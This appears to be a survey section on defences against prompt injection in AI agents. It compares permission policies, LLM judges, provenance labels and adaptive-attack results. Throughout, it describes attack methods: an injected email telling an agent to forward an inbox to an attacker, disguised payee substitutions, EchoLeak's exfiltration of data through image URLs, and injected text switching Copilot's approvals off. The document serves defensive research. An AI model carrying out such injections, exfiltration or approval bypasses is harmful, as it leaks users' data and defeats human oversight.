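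| The user's Slack name, alice | Allow posts only to alice | Applied automatically |
| Recent emails, one of which orders the agent to forward the inbox to eve@evil.com | Possibly allow sending email | Needs approval, so the approver can refuse |

The model may recognise the last email as an attack and propose nothing. If it follows the email's instructions instead, the solver still detects that the permissions would grow.

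On AgentDojo, attacks succeeded in 39.9% of cases without Progent and in 1.0% with it. On ASB, Progent lowered the rate from 70.3% to 3.9%. The agent remained about as useful as before. Only 6% of policy updates on AgentDojo needed approval. These figures come from Progent's developers. A vague request such as "deal with my emails" would give the policy model much less information for setting permissions.

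The solver can detect that permissions would grow, but not whether the reason is legitimate. In the example, Alice's list and the attacker's order both arrive as text in an email and both lead to a request for more permissions, so the approver has to tell them apart. Developers can have Progent refuse all such requests, which would make Alice's task impossible, or approve them all, which would grant the extra permissions whenever the model followed the attacker's order.

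*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) criticises Progent's policy updates on related grounds. It describes a version that uses one prompt to decide whether the policy needs an update and another to write it, and argues that the defence still depends on a model filtering out malicious instructions. This objection no longer holds if Progent uses the solver and a person or fixed rule decides on every expansion of the policy.

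#### Rules from a written policy

*NOMOS* (2026) compiles an organisation's existing written rules about what its staff can do into checks on tool calls. In AgentDojo's banking suite, these checks cut the attack success rate from 46.5% to zero for an agent running Gemma and from 44.1% to zero for one running Llama.

Harmful actions can still occur when the reported attack success rate is zero. On the banking suite, some injected payments still went to payees the user already knew, which AgentDojo doesn't count as a success for the attacker. In nine workspace cases with Llama, the agent also carried out deletions that the attacker had ordered. On the Slack suite, AgentDojo made the opposite error, reporting a 10.5% attack success rate with Llama although no harmful call had run. It had counted goals that need no tool call, or attempted calls that the software blocked.

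AgentDojo counted three harmful calls that ran, one with Gemma and two with Llama, all on the travel suite. One emailed the user's passport and card numbers to an address the user had mentioned in the request. The written policy didn't forbid this, so even a correct compilation of it would allow the call.

### A second model as the judge

Rules about tool names and arguments can't express everything a user might mean, so another group of defences uses a language model to judge whether an action serves the user's request. Task Shield, by Feiran Jia and colleagues, checks each instruction and tool call against the user's goals. DRIFT starts with a planned sequence of calls and a checklist for their parameters, then has a model decide whether a departure from the plan fits what the user wanted. DRIFT also removes suspicious instructions from the agent's memory. *Optimizing Agent Planning for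 Security and Autonomy* classes Task Shield as a heuristic defence because its verdicts have no guarantee.

*Governance Architecture for Autonomous Agent Systems* (Ge, 2026) gives unusually detailed figures for false alarms and delay. Its Layered Governance Architecture has four layers: a sandbox, a judge, limited permissions for messages between agents, and a log that nobody can rewrite. The judge receives the original task and one proposed tool call and returns "allow" or "block", so it checks individual actions rather than whole plans.

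Ge built a set of 1,081 tool calls in Chinese and machine-translated it into English. The harmful calls came from prompt injection, poisoned documents in a shared knowledge base, or malicious plug-ins. Five language models intercepted 93.0% to 98.5% of the harmful calls from the first two sources, while older classifiers, which test whether one sentence follows from another, caught fewer than 10%. Calls from malicious plug-ins were harder to catch because a plug-in can do its advertised job while also doing something else. The language models that didn't simply block most calls intercepted 75% to 94% of them.

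Some of the judges worked better in pairs, with a second model reviewing the first one's decisions:

| Judge | Harmful calls intercepted | Legitimate calls blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-14B | 98% | About 10–20% |
| Qwen3.5-9B, then Qwen2.5-14B | 94.7–95.6% | 6.0–9.7% |
| Qwen3.5-9B, then GPT-4o-mini | 91.9–92.6% | 1.9–6.7% |

Even the lower false-alarm rates are a problem when attacks are rare. Suppose an agent makes 10,000 calls and 100 of them are harmful. A judge that catches 98% of the harmful calls and blocks 10% of the others would stop 98 attacks and 990 legitimate actions, so only 9% of its alarms would be real. Ge calculates that if 1% of calls were attacks, 22.7% of the best local judge's alarms would be real. Anyone reviewing these alarms would soon get used to dismissing them.

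In a test of all four layers together, with 100 samples, the system intercepted 96% of harmful calls. The median delay was about 980 milliseconds, and the judge accounted for all but 18 of them. A job with ten checked calls would take about ten seconds longer. Ge suggests letting low-risk calls, such as reading a file, skip the judge. On cases from InjecAgent, which Ge did not write, the judges intercepted 99% to 100%.

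Ge assumed an attacker who knows nothing about the judge and doesn't adapt to it. The judge doesn't read the attacker's email directly, but a tool call's arguments can contain text from the email, so the attacker can use them to address the judge. An attacker can also supply a false account number without trying to influence the judge. If the task is to pay an invoice and the proposed call pays one, the judge has no basis for rejecting the call unless it is also given the account on file.

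### When the task depends on a document

All three approaches work best when the request determines the actions, but many useful requests don't. Tsai and Bagdasarian give the example "carry out the tasks requested in my manager's email", and Alice's to-do list is the same kind of job. The agent can't make a complete plan until it has read the email, and by then an attacker may have influenced what it plans.

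Conseca's exception shows why these tasks are difficult. The user asked the agent to perform the tasks in urgent emails, so the policy had to allow forwarding in case an urgent email asked for it, and the planted email did. The user's request alone was not enough to determine whether following that email's instructions was part of the job or an attack.

#### Plans with branches

One response is to write a branch for each possibility into the plan. The firm might ask its assistant to pay the invoice using the account on file, but to hold the payment if the supplier's latest email disputes the amount. The planner can write both branches without reading the email. An attacker who controls the email can then determine whether the assistant pays the right supplier or holds the payment, but can't add a third option.

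ACE and SPA both allow branches, but SPA's label checks would reject this plan. The decision depends on an untrusted email, so pc becomes untrusted and so does every step in both branches, including the payment to the correct account. A developer would have to lower the trust that the transfer tool requires or add endorsement, which SPA's developers leave to future work. They also suggest separate trust requirements for each argument. That would help with many rejected plans, but not this one, because the email affects whether the payment happens, not where it goes.

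Branches also can't cover a to-do list, which may contain anything. The planner would have to foresee every item.

#### Asking the user about the data

When no plan can cover every possibility, a person has to decide. Most agents that ask for permission ask before each action. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* describes Prudentia, a system from Microsoft and its collaborators that can also ask the user to endorse data as trusted. Suppose an email lists ten jobs that each need a trusted context. An agent that reads the email without endorsement must ask for approval ten times, but if the user endorses the email first, the agent can do all ten jobs after asking once.

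Asking first isn't always better, because an agent that only needs to read and summarise the email can open it without endorsement and never have to ask. Prudentia's planner chooses whether to ask first or open the email without endorsement. It has no equivalent option for secret data, because whether to reveal something usually depends on who will receive it, and the user can judge this better when asked about a specific action.

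#### Telling the planner the rules

Prudentia is built on FIDES, which keeps untrusted text in variables and checks labels before each consequential call. FIDES doesn't show its planner which calls the checks will refuse, so the planner may open a variable unnecessarily and be blocked from making a payment later. Prudentia gives the planner the policy for each tool and the current label of its context. Before opening a variable, the planner is supposed to call a planning tool to record why it needs the contents and which calls it plans to make afterwards.

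This planning step helps the agent avoid refusals, but the label checks still provide the security. A planner that ignores the advice is refused more often and gains no extra permissions.

A planner like SPA's, which gets no feedback, could also receive the policy at the start and still get only one attempt. A verdict on a particular plan could reveal how to get an unsafe version accepted, but rules that a developer wrote in advance contain nothing from an attacker. Providing these rules might recover some of the plans that SPA rejects, though SPA's developers haven't tried it.

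To measure the benefit, the Prudentia team counted how often an agent needs a person. Let v(τᵢ) be the number of calls in the i-th run that break the policy and so need approval. For n tasks, they define:

approval load = the sum of v(τᵢ) over all completed tasks

TCR@k = (number of tasks completed with v(τᵢ) ≤ k) / n

TCR stands for task completion rate. TCR@0 counts only the tasks that the agent completes without asking anyone, and TCR@∞ allows any number of approvals. These are the AgentDojo results with OpenAI's o3-mini, averaged over five runs:

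| Agent | Approval load | TCR@0 |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent that asks before every consequential call | 48.2 | 24.3% |
| Ordinary agent with label checks | 32.4 | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | About 17 | 59.1% |

With o4-mini, Prudentia needed 19.2 approvals and FIDES needed 36.8, but FIDES completed slightly more tasks when approvals were unlimited (75.7% against 73.2%). The choice between endorsing data and approving actions mattered most for tasks that depend on a document, where Prudentia cut the approval load by a factor of up to 2.5.

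These measures also change how to interpret the utility losses of label-based defences. Earlier studies compared defended agents, which could never ask for help, with undefended agents, which never needed it. That comparison is fair for a firm that would otherwise let its agent act freely. For a firm that already requires approval for every payment, the relevant baseline is 24.3%, and label checks let the agent do more by itself.

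Prudentia did best on WASP, a benchmark for agents that use a web browser. Across four models, attacks diverted an ordinary agent in 14.6% to 61.1% of cases. They never diverted Prudentia, which needed no approvals and completed at least as many tasks. But users only asked the agent to post a comment or upvote a post, so it never had to act on a page's content.

No attacks succeeded on AgentDojo, but this result depends partly on the assumption that the person reviewing a request will recognise and stop an injection. The paper warns of approval fatigue. Asking users for endorsement less often should help, but each endorsement then covers more. If nine of the ten tasks in an email are genuine and the tenth is a payment to an attacker's account, a user who endorses the email without noticing the payment has approved all ten.

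## Tests against attackers who adapt

Most of the low attack success rates in the earlier experiments come from attacks written before the defence existed. A real attacker can watch an attempt fail, change the wording and send another email.

A little notation shows how much this can matter. Let s(a, c) be 1 if attack text a succeeds in test case c, and 0 if it fails. A fixed benchmark chooses one text, a₀, and reports its average over n cases. If an attacker can try many texts, including a₀, then:

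(1/n) Σ s(a₀, c) ≤ maxₐ (1/n) Σ s(a, c) ≤ (1/n) Σ maxₐ s(a, c)

The left side shows the benchmark score. The middle shows the score of an attacker who plants the single best text where many agents will read it, and the right side shows the score of an attacker who tailors a text to each case. Against the same defence, attacks can score zero on the left and close to 100% on the right.

A fixed attack may also fail for reasons unrelated to the defence. Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) found in *The Attacker Moves Second* that AgentDojo's standard attack never succeeded against GPT-5 Mini, even with no defence. A search for better wordings succeeded in 75% of cases. A defence that did nothing could therefore have looked perfect on that model against the standard attack.

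### Twelve published defences

Nasr and colleagues attacked twelve defences, ten that address prompt injection and two that try to stop users from getting harmful content out of a model. In the original evaluations, attack success rates were near zero for most of the defences. The new attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the twelve.

The attacks used gradients, reinforcement learning, a search guided by a language model, or people. In each case, the attacker tried a text, observed the result and revised the text. The team assumed that the attacker knows how the defence works and has a lot of computing time, as is standard in computer security.

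Three of the twelve defences (Spotlighting, StruQ and MetaSecAlign) divide the model's input into zones. Attacks on Spotlighting succeeded more than 95% of the time. StruQ failed in every case tested, usually because the attacker's text imitated a system message. MetaSecAlign, a model trained to ignore instructions in the data part of its input, had a reported attack success rate of 2% on AgentDojo, which the search raised to 96%. These results are strong evidence against relying on any zone that only the model enforces.

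The table shows results for seven defences on 80 AgentDojo cases from the Slack, travel and workspace suites. The search could make up to 800 attempts per case, and a case counts as a successful attack if any attempt worked. The figures for tasks completed cover all 97 user tasks.

| Defence | Tasks completed, Gemini 2.5 Pro | Fixed attack, Gemini 2.5 Pro | Search, Gemini 2.5 Pro | Fixed attack, GPT-5 Mini | Search, GPT-5 Mini |
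|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 74% | 30% | 100% | 0% | 75% |
| Spotlighting | 75% | 28% | 99% | 0% | 47% |
| Prompt Sandwiching (repeats the user's request) | 73% | 21% | 95% | 0% | 69% |
| Protect AI (classifier) | 39% | 15% | 90% | 0% | 81% |
| PIGuard (classifier) | 39% | 0% | 71% | 0% | 49% |
| PromptGuard (classifier) | 72% | 26% | 94% | 0% | 75% |
| Model Armor (Google's filter) | 59% | 28% | 90% | 0% | 56% |
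| MELON (compares two runs) | 58% | 0% | 89% | 0% | 71% |

With Gemini 2.5 Pro, the median successful search took 14 attempts against Spotlighting and 13 against no defence, so Spotlighting's markers barely slowed the attacker. They helped more on GPT-5 Mini, although Nasr and colleagues expect that an attacker with a larger budget would overcome them there too. PIGuard resisted attacks best on Gemini, but the agent completed only about half as many tasks with it.

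MELON runs the agent a second time with a harmless request in place of the user's and looks for tool calls that appear in both runs. This defense depends partly on the attacker not knowing the harmless request. On Llama 3.3 70B, the attack search succeeded in 76% of cases when the attacker knew nothing about MELON and in 95% when the attacker knew how it worked. This agrees with the FATH experiments, where a secret in the model's context gave only limited protection.

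The team also ran a contest with more than 500 participants and $20,000 in prizes. Participants and the search both attempted 29 of the scenarios. At least one participant succeeded in each of them, while the search succeeded in 69%. The best participant who tried all 29 succeeded in 75%. Many submissions failed, especially against the GPT-5 models, but an attacker needs only one to work.

Zhan, Fang and colleagues had already reported similar results in *Adaptive Attacks Break Defenses Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks on LLM Agents*. They bypassed all eight defences they tested, with attack success rates above 50%.

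The outcome still depends on the attacker's method and the target. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* tested undefended agents and found that search succeeded in 45.2% of cases on Qwen3-4B, a small open model, while a gradient method succeeded in 24.1%. Search succeeded in only about 5% of cases on GPT-5, and texts tuned on small models did not transfer to it. An attacker who can't practise on the real target is therefore much weaker than the one Nasr and colleagues assumed.

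Nasr and colleagues did not test CaMeL or two other defences that fix the plan or the set of tools before the agent reads outside text. Most of their attacks could not have succeeded against such a design, because the injected text never reaches the planner. Their results are therefore not evidence for or against provenance labels and plan gates. They recommend testing these defences on tasks where the right actions depend on what the agent reads.

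### Defences that limit actions

*AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) includes such systems in an adaptive test of ten defences on five models. The test uses three task suites from AgentDojo and three from AgentDyn, a benchmark of more open-ended tasks.

Their attacker is weaker than the one in the previous study because it doesn't know which defence is active, can't see the agent's reasoning, and learns only how many of its attempts succeeded. A language model uses those counts to revise the attack text over six rounds. A single text has to work across several users' requests, so this test measures the middle quantity in the inequality above, while the search by Nasr and colleagues measures the one on the right.

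These are the results on AgentDojo's banking, Slack and travel suites, which contain 57 user tasks and 389 attack cases. The first three columns of figures are for GPT-4o-mini. The last column gives the range of AutoDojo's attack success rates on GPT-5.4-mini, Gemini 2.5 Flash, DeepSeek-v4-Flash and Claude Haiku 4.5.

| Family | Defence | Tasks completed, no attack | Fixed attack | AutoDojo | AutoDojo, other models |
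|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | None | 66.7% | 58.6% | 52.4% | 1.8–34.7% |
| Prompt | Reminder | 68.4% | 39.3% | 40.4% | 1.0–29.6% |
| Prompt | Spotlighting | 59.6% | 51.7% | 46.8% | 1.8–36.2% |
| Filter | PromptGuard | 63.2% | 54.2% | 49.4% | 1.0–30.1% |
| Filter | PIGuard | 43.9% | 0.0% | 28.0% | 0.8–10.5% |
| Filter | ProtectAI | 47.4% | 7.2% | 15.4% | 1.3–7.2% |
| Filter | DataFilter | 64.9% | 12.6% | 33.4% | 1.5–26.5% |
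| System | Progent | 63.2% | 8.2% | 7.7% | 0.5–4.6% |
| System | DRIFT | 49.1% | 2.6% | 6.4% | 1.0–9.0% |
| System | CaMeL | 26.3% | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.3–1.8% |
| System | ROPE | 59.6% | 6.4% | 4.4% | 0.3–3.9% |

Tests with fixed attacks can be misleading. PIGuard blocked every standard injection on all five models, but AutoDojo raised the attack success rate on GPT-4o-mini to 28.0%. In one successful banking attack, the injected text contained no command. It presented the attacker's account number as a payment detail in an ordinary-looking bill, so the classifier let it through and the agent paid. The false account number in the supplier's email would work the same way.

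AutoDojo did worse than the fixed attack in some rows because Ma and colleagues required it to return a newly written text. A real attacker could use whichever attack worked better.

#### CaMeL, ROPE and DRIFT

CaMeL was the most secure of the ten defenses, and the few attacks that succeeded against it were all in the travel suite. But it also lost the most utility on four of the five models. On GPT-4o-mini, it completed 15 of the 57 tasks, compared with 38 for the undefended agent.

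With DeepSeek-v4-Flash and the developers' own code and policies, CaMeL completed 38.6% of the tasks and let through 0.5% of the attacks. In the *PACE* rerun with the same model, it completed 60% of the tasks and let through 28% of the attacks. Looser policies in the rerun could explain both increases, although the suites and attacks also differ.

CaMeL's protection depends on outside text never reaching a planner. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* describes how this can fail when agents exchange messages. An attacker plants an instruction in a database, one agent passes it on, and the email agent's planner reads it directly and sends out private data.

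ROPE checks where each sensitive argument came from and blocks the call if the value comes from untrusted content instead of the user. With ROPE, the GPT-4o-mini agent completed 34 tasks, four fewer than the undefended agent, and no banking attack succeeded. This is the best evidence so far that provenance checks can withstand an adaptive attacker without a large loss of utility. Several people worked on both AutoDojo and ROPE, so an independent test would be valuable.

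DRIFT was less steady. AutoDojo more than doubled the attack success rate against DRIFT on every model, though the rate never exceeded 9.0%. Ma and colleagues attribute the increase to the language model that DRIFT uses to judge instructions while the agent runs, since an attacker can try to mislead that model.

#### Progent

AutoDojo's adaptive attack succeeded against Progent 7.7% of the time, compared with 8.2% for the fixed attack. But to save money, AutoDojo developed its attack texts against a version of Progent in which a different language model wrote the permissions, while the final evaluation used GPT-4o. An attacker who practised on the GPT-4o version might do better.

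Narisetty and colleagues, who work at LaunchSafe, aimed an attack specifically at the model that writes Progent's permissions. Their text presented the harmful action as a necessary step that somebody had already approved. They used Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, both as the agent and to write the permissions. These are averages over three runs:

| | Undefended, standard attack | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
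|---|---|---|---|
| Attack success, banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
| Attack success, Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Attack success, workspace | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Attack success, mean | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |
| Tasks completed under attack, mean | 45.2% | 27.1% | 25.8% |

The adaptive attack did worse than the standard one, but this may be due more to the attack than to Progent. Narisetty and colleagues suspect that the softer wording made the agent less likely to obey. They used only eight user tasks per suite and one attack template. No attack worked in the workspace suite even without a defence, so that suite couldn't be used to compare the conditions. Progent also needed about 15 times as many model calls per task.

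LaunchSafe builds security tools on the same principle as Progent, so it has a commercial interest in the result. But its figures agree with the 0.5% to 4.2% that Progent's developers reported under their own adaptive attacks.

Neither test used an attacker who both had full knowledge of Progent and could search at length for a successful attack. Attackers with both advantages broke most of the twelve defences that Nasr and colleagues tested, so Progent's results are encouraging but incomplete.

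### Vague requests are easier to exploit

Ma and colleagues also sorted the user tasks into three groups by how much each request leaves to outside content. A fully specified request gives the action and all its details, such as a new address to save. In the middle group, the user names the action but the agent has to look up some details, as when it pays a bill whose amount and payee are in a file. In the vaguest group, the user asks the agent to do whatever a document says.

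These are AutoDojo's attack success rates on GPT-4o-mini:

| What the request leaves open | Cases | No defence | PIGuard | Progent | DRIFT | ROPE |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing | 127 | 32.3% | 17.3% | 3.1% | 3.9% | 3.1% |
| Details of the action | 238 | 60.5% | 31.1% | 10.1% | 8.0% | 4.6% |
| The action itself | 24 | 79.2% | 54.2% | 8.3% | 4.2% | 8.3% |

If the user has told the agent to follow a document, an attacker can write text that looks like a normal part of it. A filter that searches for commands then has little to detect. The fixed attack produced the same ordering on the undefended agent, so the weakness isn't an artefact of AutoDojo.

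The vaguest group contains only four user tasks, each paired with several attacks. The Wilson formula gives a range of 35% to 72% for PIGuard's 13 successes in 24 cases, but the real uncertainty is greater because the cases share tasks. AgentDyn has twelve tasks of this kind. Its GitHub and shopping suites showed the same pattern, but its daily-life suite did not.

Progent and DRIFT have low values in the last row partly because they often allow only reading on these tasks. This blocks the attacker, but also any legitimate change requested in the document.

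#### Attacks that leave the action unchanged

The middle group includes the firm's request to pay an invoice. In this group, an attacker can change a detail of the action the user wanted instead of adding a new one. Wang and colleagues built the AgentPI benchmark around this problem and tested eight defences on GPT-4o-mini. Its attacks don't adapt to the defence, but the team wrote them to fit each type of task.

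Progent and MELON stopped nearly all attacks that switched the agent to a different tool or abused a user's instruction to follow a document. They gave little protection when the attacker changed an argument, misled the agent about an if-then condition or corrupted a calculation. In those cases, the agent calls a permitted tool for a purpose that seems to match the request.

Progent also completed fewer than 30% of AgentPI's legitimate tasks. It ran faster than the undefended agent only because it refused so many tasks early.

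### How much work the defences block

AgentDojo underestimates how much usefulness an agent loses when a defence holds it to its first plan. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) reports that only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to revise its plan after reading something.

All 60 AgentDyn tasks require such revisions, and they take an average of 7.1 steps, compared with 3.5 in AgentDojo. Outside text also contains useful instructions, such as a checkout page's instruction to log in first, so a defence can't succeed by ignoring every instruction in that text.

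These are the results with GPT-4o and AgentDojo's standard attack:

| Defence | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack | Attack success |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 53.3% | 55.5% | 37.8% |
| Prompt Sandwiching | 63.3% | 56.1% | 31.2% |
| Spotlighting | 55.0% | 52.2% | 27.6% |
| ProtectAI | 0.0% | 0.6% | 0.9% |
| PIGuard | 10.0% | 1.5% | 1.7% |
| PromptGuard 2 | 60.0% | 20.8% | 27.2% |
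| Tool Filter | 8.3% | 4.9% | 4.2% |
| CaMeL | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Progent | 6.7% | 5.8% | 1.7% |
| DRIFT | 30.0% | 27.1% | 0.8% |

The defences with the lowest attack success rates also blocked most of the agent's legitimate work. Tool Filter, which selects tools at the start, removed some that the agent needed later. Progent's permission-writing model made mistakes with the larger set of tools, and these accumulated over long tasks. CaMeL completed no tasks, much as in the *PACE* rerun.

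The test may make approval-based systems look worse than they would in practice, because Li and colleagues instructed the agents to finish every task without asking the user for confirmation. CaMeL and Progent can both refer a blocked action to a person, so the agents might have completed some of these tasks with a few approvals.

Meta SecAlign seemed to offer the best compromise, completing 55.0% of the tasks with an attack success rate of 9.0%. Li and colleagues suggested that this kind of training might be the more practical approach. But Nasr and colleagues broke the same defence in 96% of cases on AgentDojo, so its good score on a fixed attack is weak evidence of how it would perform against a determined attacker.

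Ma and colleagues ran AutoDojo on the same tasks with GPT-4o-mini. With Progent, the agent completed 6.7% of them when there was no attack. Under attack, it carried out the attacker's goal in 12.7% of cases and the user's task in 12.0%. With ROPE, the agent completed 43.3%, close to the undefended agent's 46.7%, and attacks succeeded 2.9% of the time. ROPE reduced completion more with Gemini 2.5 Flash, from 36.7% to 25.0%.

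Progent's utility loss therefore varies between tests. It was 3.5 percentage points in AutoDojo's AgentDojo runs with GPT-4o-mini, 18 in the LaunchSafe reproduction and 47 on AgentDyn with GPT-4o. Each figure compares defended and undefended agents in the same setup, but the tasks and the models that wrote the permissions differed across the three tests, so a firm would need to measure the loss on its own work.

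### Agents that work through a command line

Checks on tool calls are easiest to write when each tool has one narrow purpose. *INFUSE* (Nguyen, Guo and colleagues, 2026) tested agents that do everything by running shell commands, including editing files, installing software and contacting servers. A rule that permits the shell tool permits very little or almost everything, depending on how well the checking software can interpret each command.

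Across 19 models, attacks succeeded in an average of 19.6% of runs according to a language-model judge, and 15.4% according to automatic checks of the results. Rates for individual models ranged from 3.2% to 41.9%. Separate classifiers built to screen chat messages for unsafe content gave limited protection, and attacks still succeeded about 44% of the time on a set of especially vulnerable cases.

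Stronger warnings in the prompt did better, cutting attack success from 58.2% to 14.3%. But most of the attacks in this benchmark did not adapt to the defence, and prompt-based defences are among those that adaptive attackers have broken most easily.

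## Code audits, incidents and shipped products

Most of the defences tested so far are research prototypes, and a good result on AgentDojo doesn't mean that any product uses the idea. Framework source code, flaws in live products and the makers' security pages give some idea of how far developers apply the four criteria.

### An audit of three frameworks

Many developers use a framework such as LangChain or LlamaIndex, which runs the functions the model calls, instead of writing the agent loop themselves. They can add the Stripe Agent Toolkit to let an agent handle payments through Stripe. Mellafe Zuvic (2026), in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, audited the public source code of all three, along with LangChain's sister project LangGraph.

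The audit distinguishes capability gating, which decides what tools an agent has, from per-call authorisation, which decides whether one call may run with the account number and amount it contains. Mellafe Zuvic used a fixed version of each codebase so that others can check the reading. He traced what happens after the model emits a tool call to see whether the software checks the actual values against a policy before the tool runs, and refuses the call if the check fails.

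All three limit which tools the agent has. None checks the values by default:

- LangChain and LangGraph look up the tool by name, usually check that the arguments have the right format, and run it. A developer can add a step that asks a person first, but the framework doesn't require one.
- LlamaIndex works in much the same way. If the model names a tool that doesn't exist, the software tells the model so and carries on, without treating it as a security event.
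- The Stripe toolkit has a list of permitted actions, and Stripe's restricted keys narrow it further. Within those limits, the toolkit forwards whatever amount, customer or redirect address the model supplies.

The attacker's account number in the supplier email has the right format, so it would pass. Mellafe Zuvic calls this a confused deputy, a term from the 1980s for a program that lets someone who lacks its authority direct it.

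To confirm the reading of the code, Mellafe Zuvic fed LangChain a fixed model output that called for changing a merchant's payout account to the attacker's. LangChain made the change in a mock payment system, and LlamaIndex failed a similar test. Mellafe Zuvic doesn't claim a vulnerability in any of the frameworks, because their designs leave it to the developer to check such actions.

An audit of defaults can't show how many developers add the check themselves. Stripe also runs a remote service whose code isn't public, and it may check more than the toolkit does.

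Dong, Lu and colleagues (2026), in *The Claws in Plain Sight*, found a similar gap with private data. They asked five DeepSeek and Claude configurations to prepare a product offer, and added a memo falsely claiming that the tool needed the customer's age, gender, income bracket and occupation. The prompt restricted the use of these details in 90 sessions, but the models still put protected details into the tool call in 40 of them. The agent was allowed to use the tool and the calls were well formed, so capability gating would have allowed all 40 calls. The profiles were synthetic and no data left the test machine.

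#### ScopeGate

Mellafe Zuvic proposes ScopeGate, a short program that sits between the model and the tools and applies five rules to each call:

1. Scope: the policy must list the tool.
2. Authorisation: each restricted argument must be on a list of approved values, such as verified payout accounts.
3. Money: the amount must be an ordinary number between zero and a ceiling.
4. Idempotency: where the policy requires it, a tool with side effects needs a key from trusted software, which limits repeated calls.
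5. Default deny: ScopeGate refuses any call that fails a rule or causes an error.

The policy must come from the operator, and no model may write or extend any part of it, even offline. This is stricter than Progent or Conseca, whose rules come from a language model.

ScopeGate refused all 48 hand-written attempts to bypass it, including some that used look-alike characters or misspelled tool names. These tests also exposed a bug in an earlier prototype, which accepted the special value "not a number" as a payment amount. In another test, the model GLM-5.2 had 40 tries and was told the reason for every refusal. It produced 29 unauthorised calls. ScopeGate refused them all, as expected, because persuasion can't add an account to its approved list.

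The tests provide much less evidence about usefulness. ScopeGate refused none of the 10 legitimate calls in the main control, but by the Wilson formula that result is consistent with a true refusal rate for such calls of up to 28%. A firm would also have to keep the list current, and its assistant couldn't pay a new supplier until someone added the supplier's account.

ScopeGate doesn't meet any of the four criteria in full. It checks single calls rather than plans and doesn't record where values came from. A list of approved payees can replace a provenance label when the firm knows its payees in advance, but no such list exists for the body of an email or the text of a report.

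In a companion test of 27 models, Mellafe Zuvic found that cheaper models attempted the attacker's action in 60.3% of cases on average, compared with 18.9% for flagship models. These were attempts in a sandbox, and one person wrote the attacks, but the results suggest that a firm using a cheaper model has more need of a check outside the model.

### Flaws in live products

#### EchoLeak

In June 2025 the security company Aim Security disclosed EchoLeak, a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that can read a user's mail and files. The attacker only had to send an email containing hidden instructions. When the user later asked Copilot a question, Copilot could retrieve that email together with internal documents. The instructions made Copilot put confidential details into the web address of an image in its reply. The user's app loaded the image automatically, which sent the details to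 the attacker. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), an entry in the vulnerability database of Spain's national cybersecurity institute, rates the flaw critical, at 9.3 out of 10.

*EchoLeak*, a case study by Reddy and Gujral (2025), describes an attack that got past three defenses Microsoft already had in place: a classifier for injected text, a filter that removes outside links from replies, and a browser rule about which sites may supply images. The browser rule failed because a Microsoft service on the approved list would fetch outside addresses on request.

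EchoLeak succeeded because the system lacked context zoning. A stranger's email shared one context with the firm's internal files, and nothing restricted what the combined text could be used for. Provenance labels would also have helped. Under the rules that Costa and colleagues use, the reply would have been labeled both untrusted and secret, so software that checked labels before loading an image would have blocked the request to an outside server. Dongol's theorems do not cover the route that EchoLeak used, and leave the display software to secure it.

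Microsoft deployed a fix on its own servers in May 2025, before the disclosure, and customers didn't have to do anything. Reddy and Gujral report that Copilot now strips certain links and images from outside content, and that Microsoft reportedly added options to keep external messages out of Copilot in some situations. Stripping links and images repairs a filter, and keeping external messages out creates a simple context zone, though the assistant may then miss relevant mail.

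Their main recommendation is to separate trusted and untrusted content, but the example they give is a form of spotlighting, a defense that Nasr and colleagues broke.

#### The Copilot approval flaw

A second flaw from 2025, which Dongol modelled, is the closest real case to an attacker switching approvals off. GitHub Copilot's coding agent normally asks before it runs a command. Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot*, an account by a researcher who found the flaw, reports that the agent could edit files in the project folder without asking, including the one that held the approval setting. Injected text could therefore make the agent turn on automatic approval and then run the attacker's commands.

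MITRE's *GitHub Copilot and Visual Studio Remote Code Execution Vulnerability* (2025), the official record of the flaw, gives a severity of 7.8 and lists Visual Studio 2022 as affected from version 17.14.0 until the fix in 17.14.12. The researcher reported the flaw on 29 June 2025 to Microsoft, which fixed it in August.

The software did not meet the criterion of signed intent for mode changes, because it accepted a new mode without checking who had ordered it. *August 2025 (version 1.104)* (2025), Microsoft's release notes for the editor VS Code, describes a related change that makes the agent ask the user before it edits certain files, so a person can stop the model from changing the setting. Microsoft did not respond with signatures.

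The flaw is strong evidence that an agent shouldn't be able to change its own mode, but it doesn't show that cryptography is necessary. Making the settings file read-only for the agent would also have worked. Signatures may be more useful where several programs can write the same settings. Embrace The Red points out that developers often run more than one agent in a project, and that one agent could overwrite another's configuration. A signed setting would fail the check no matter which program had changed it.

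#### An overreach without an attacker

Agents also exceed their authority when nobody is attacking them. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes three actions by Claude Code, the company's coding agent, that an automatic checker stopped during internal use. In one, an employee asked for read-only access to billing data, and Claude tried to assign a role with full administrative control of the cloud account. In another, Claude tried to kill processes across roughly two thousand pods (groups of running programs) and queued deletions that would have destroyed training jobs on hundreds of GPUs.

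The billing case is an unauthorised mode change from read access to full control, and all the text that led to it may have been trusted. If so, context zones and provenance labels aimed at outsiders would not have caught it. A rule comparing the requested permission with the one being granted would have caught it, as would a signature covering only read access.

#### What can be counted

Researchers found both of the 2025 flaws. Microsoft knew of no attack that used EchoLeak, and the US cybersecurity agency CISA recorded no exploitation of the approval flaw when it assessed it in August 2025. The two cases prove that such attacks can work on widely used products, but they can't support an attack success rate, because nobody has published how many emails Copilot processed safely or how many similar flaws remain unreported. There is also no similar product with context zones to compare them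 with.

Official vulnerability databases don't help much with counting either, because their categories describe text that the software failed to clean, not missing zones or unsigned mode changes. The approval flaw is listed as command injection. Microsoft's record for EchoLeak, as reproduced by the database GCVE, uses a category for output that a program passes on without neutralising special elements.

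In May 2026 Microsoft published *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), an advisory for a different flaw in the same family of products as EchoLeak. Information disclosure can have many causes, so the title is not evidence that this flaw resembles EchoLeak.

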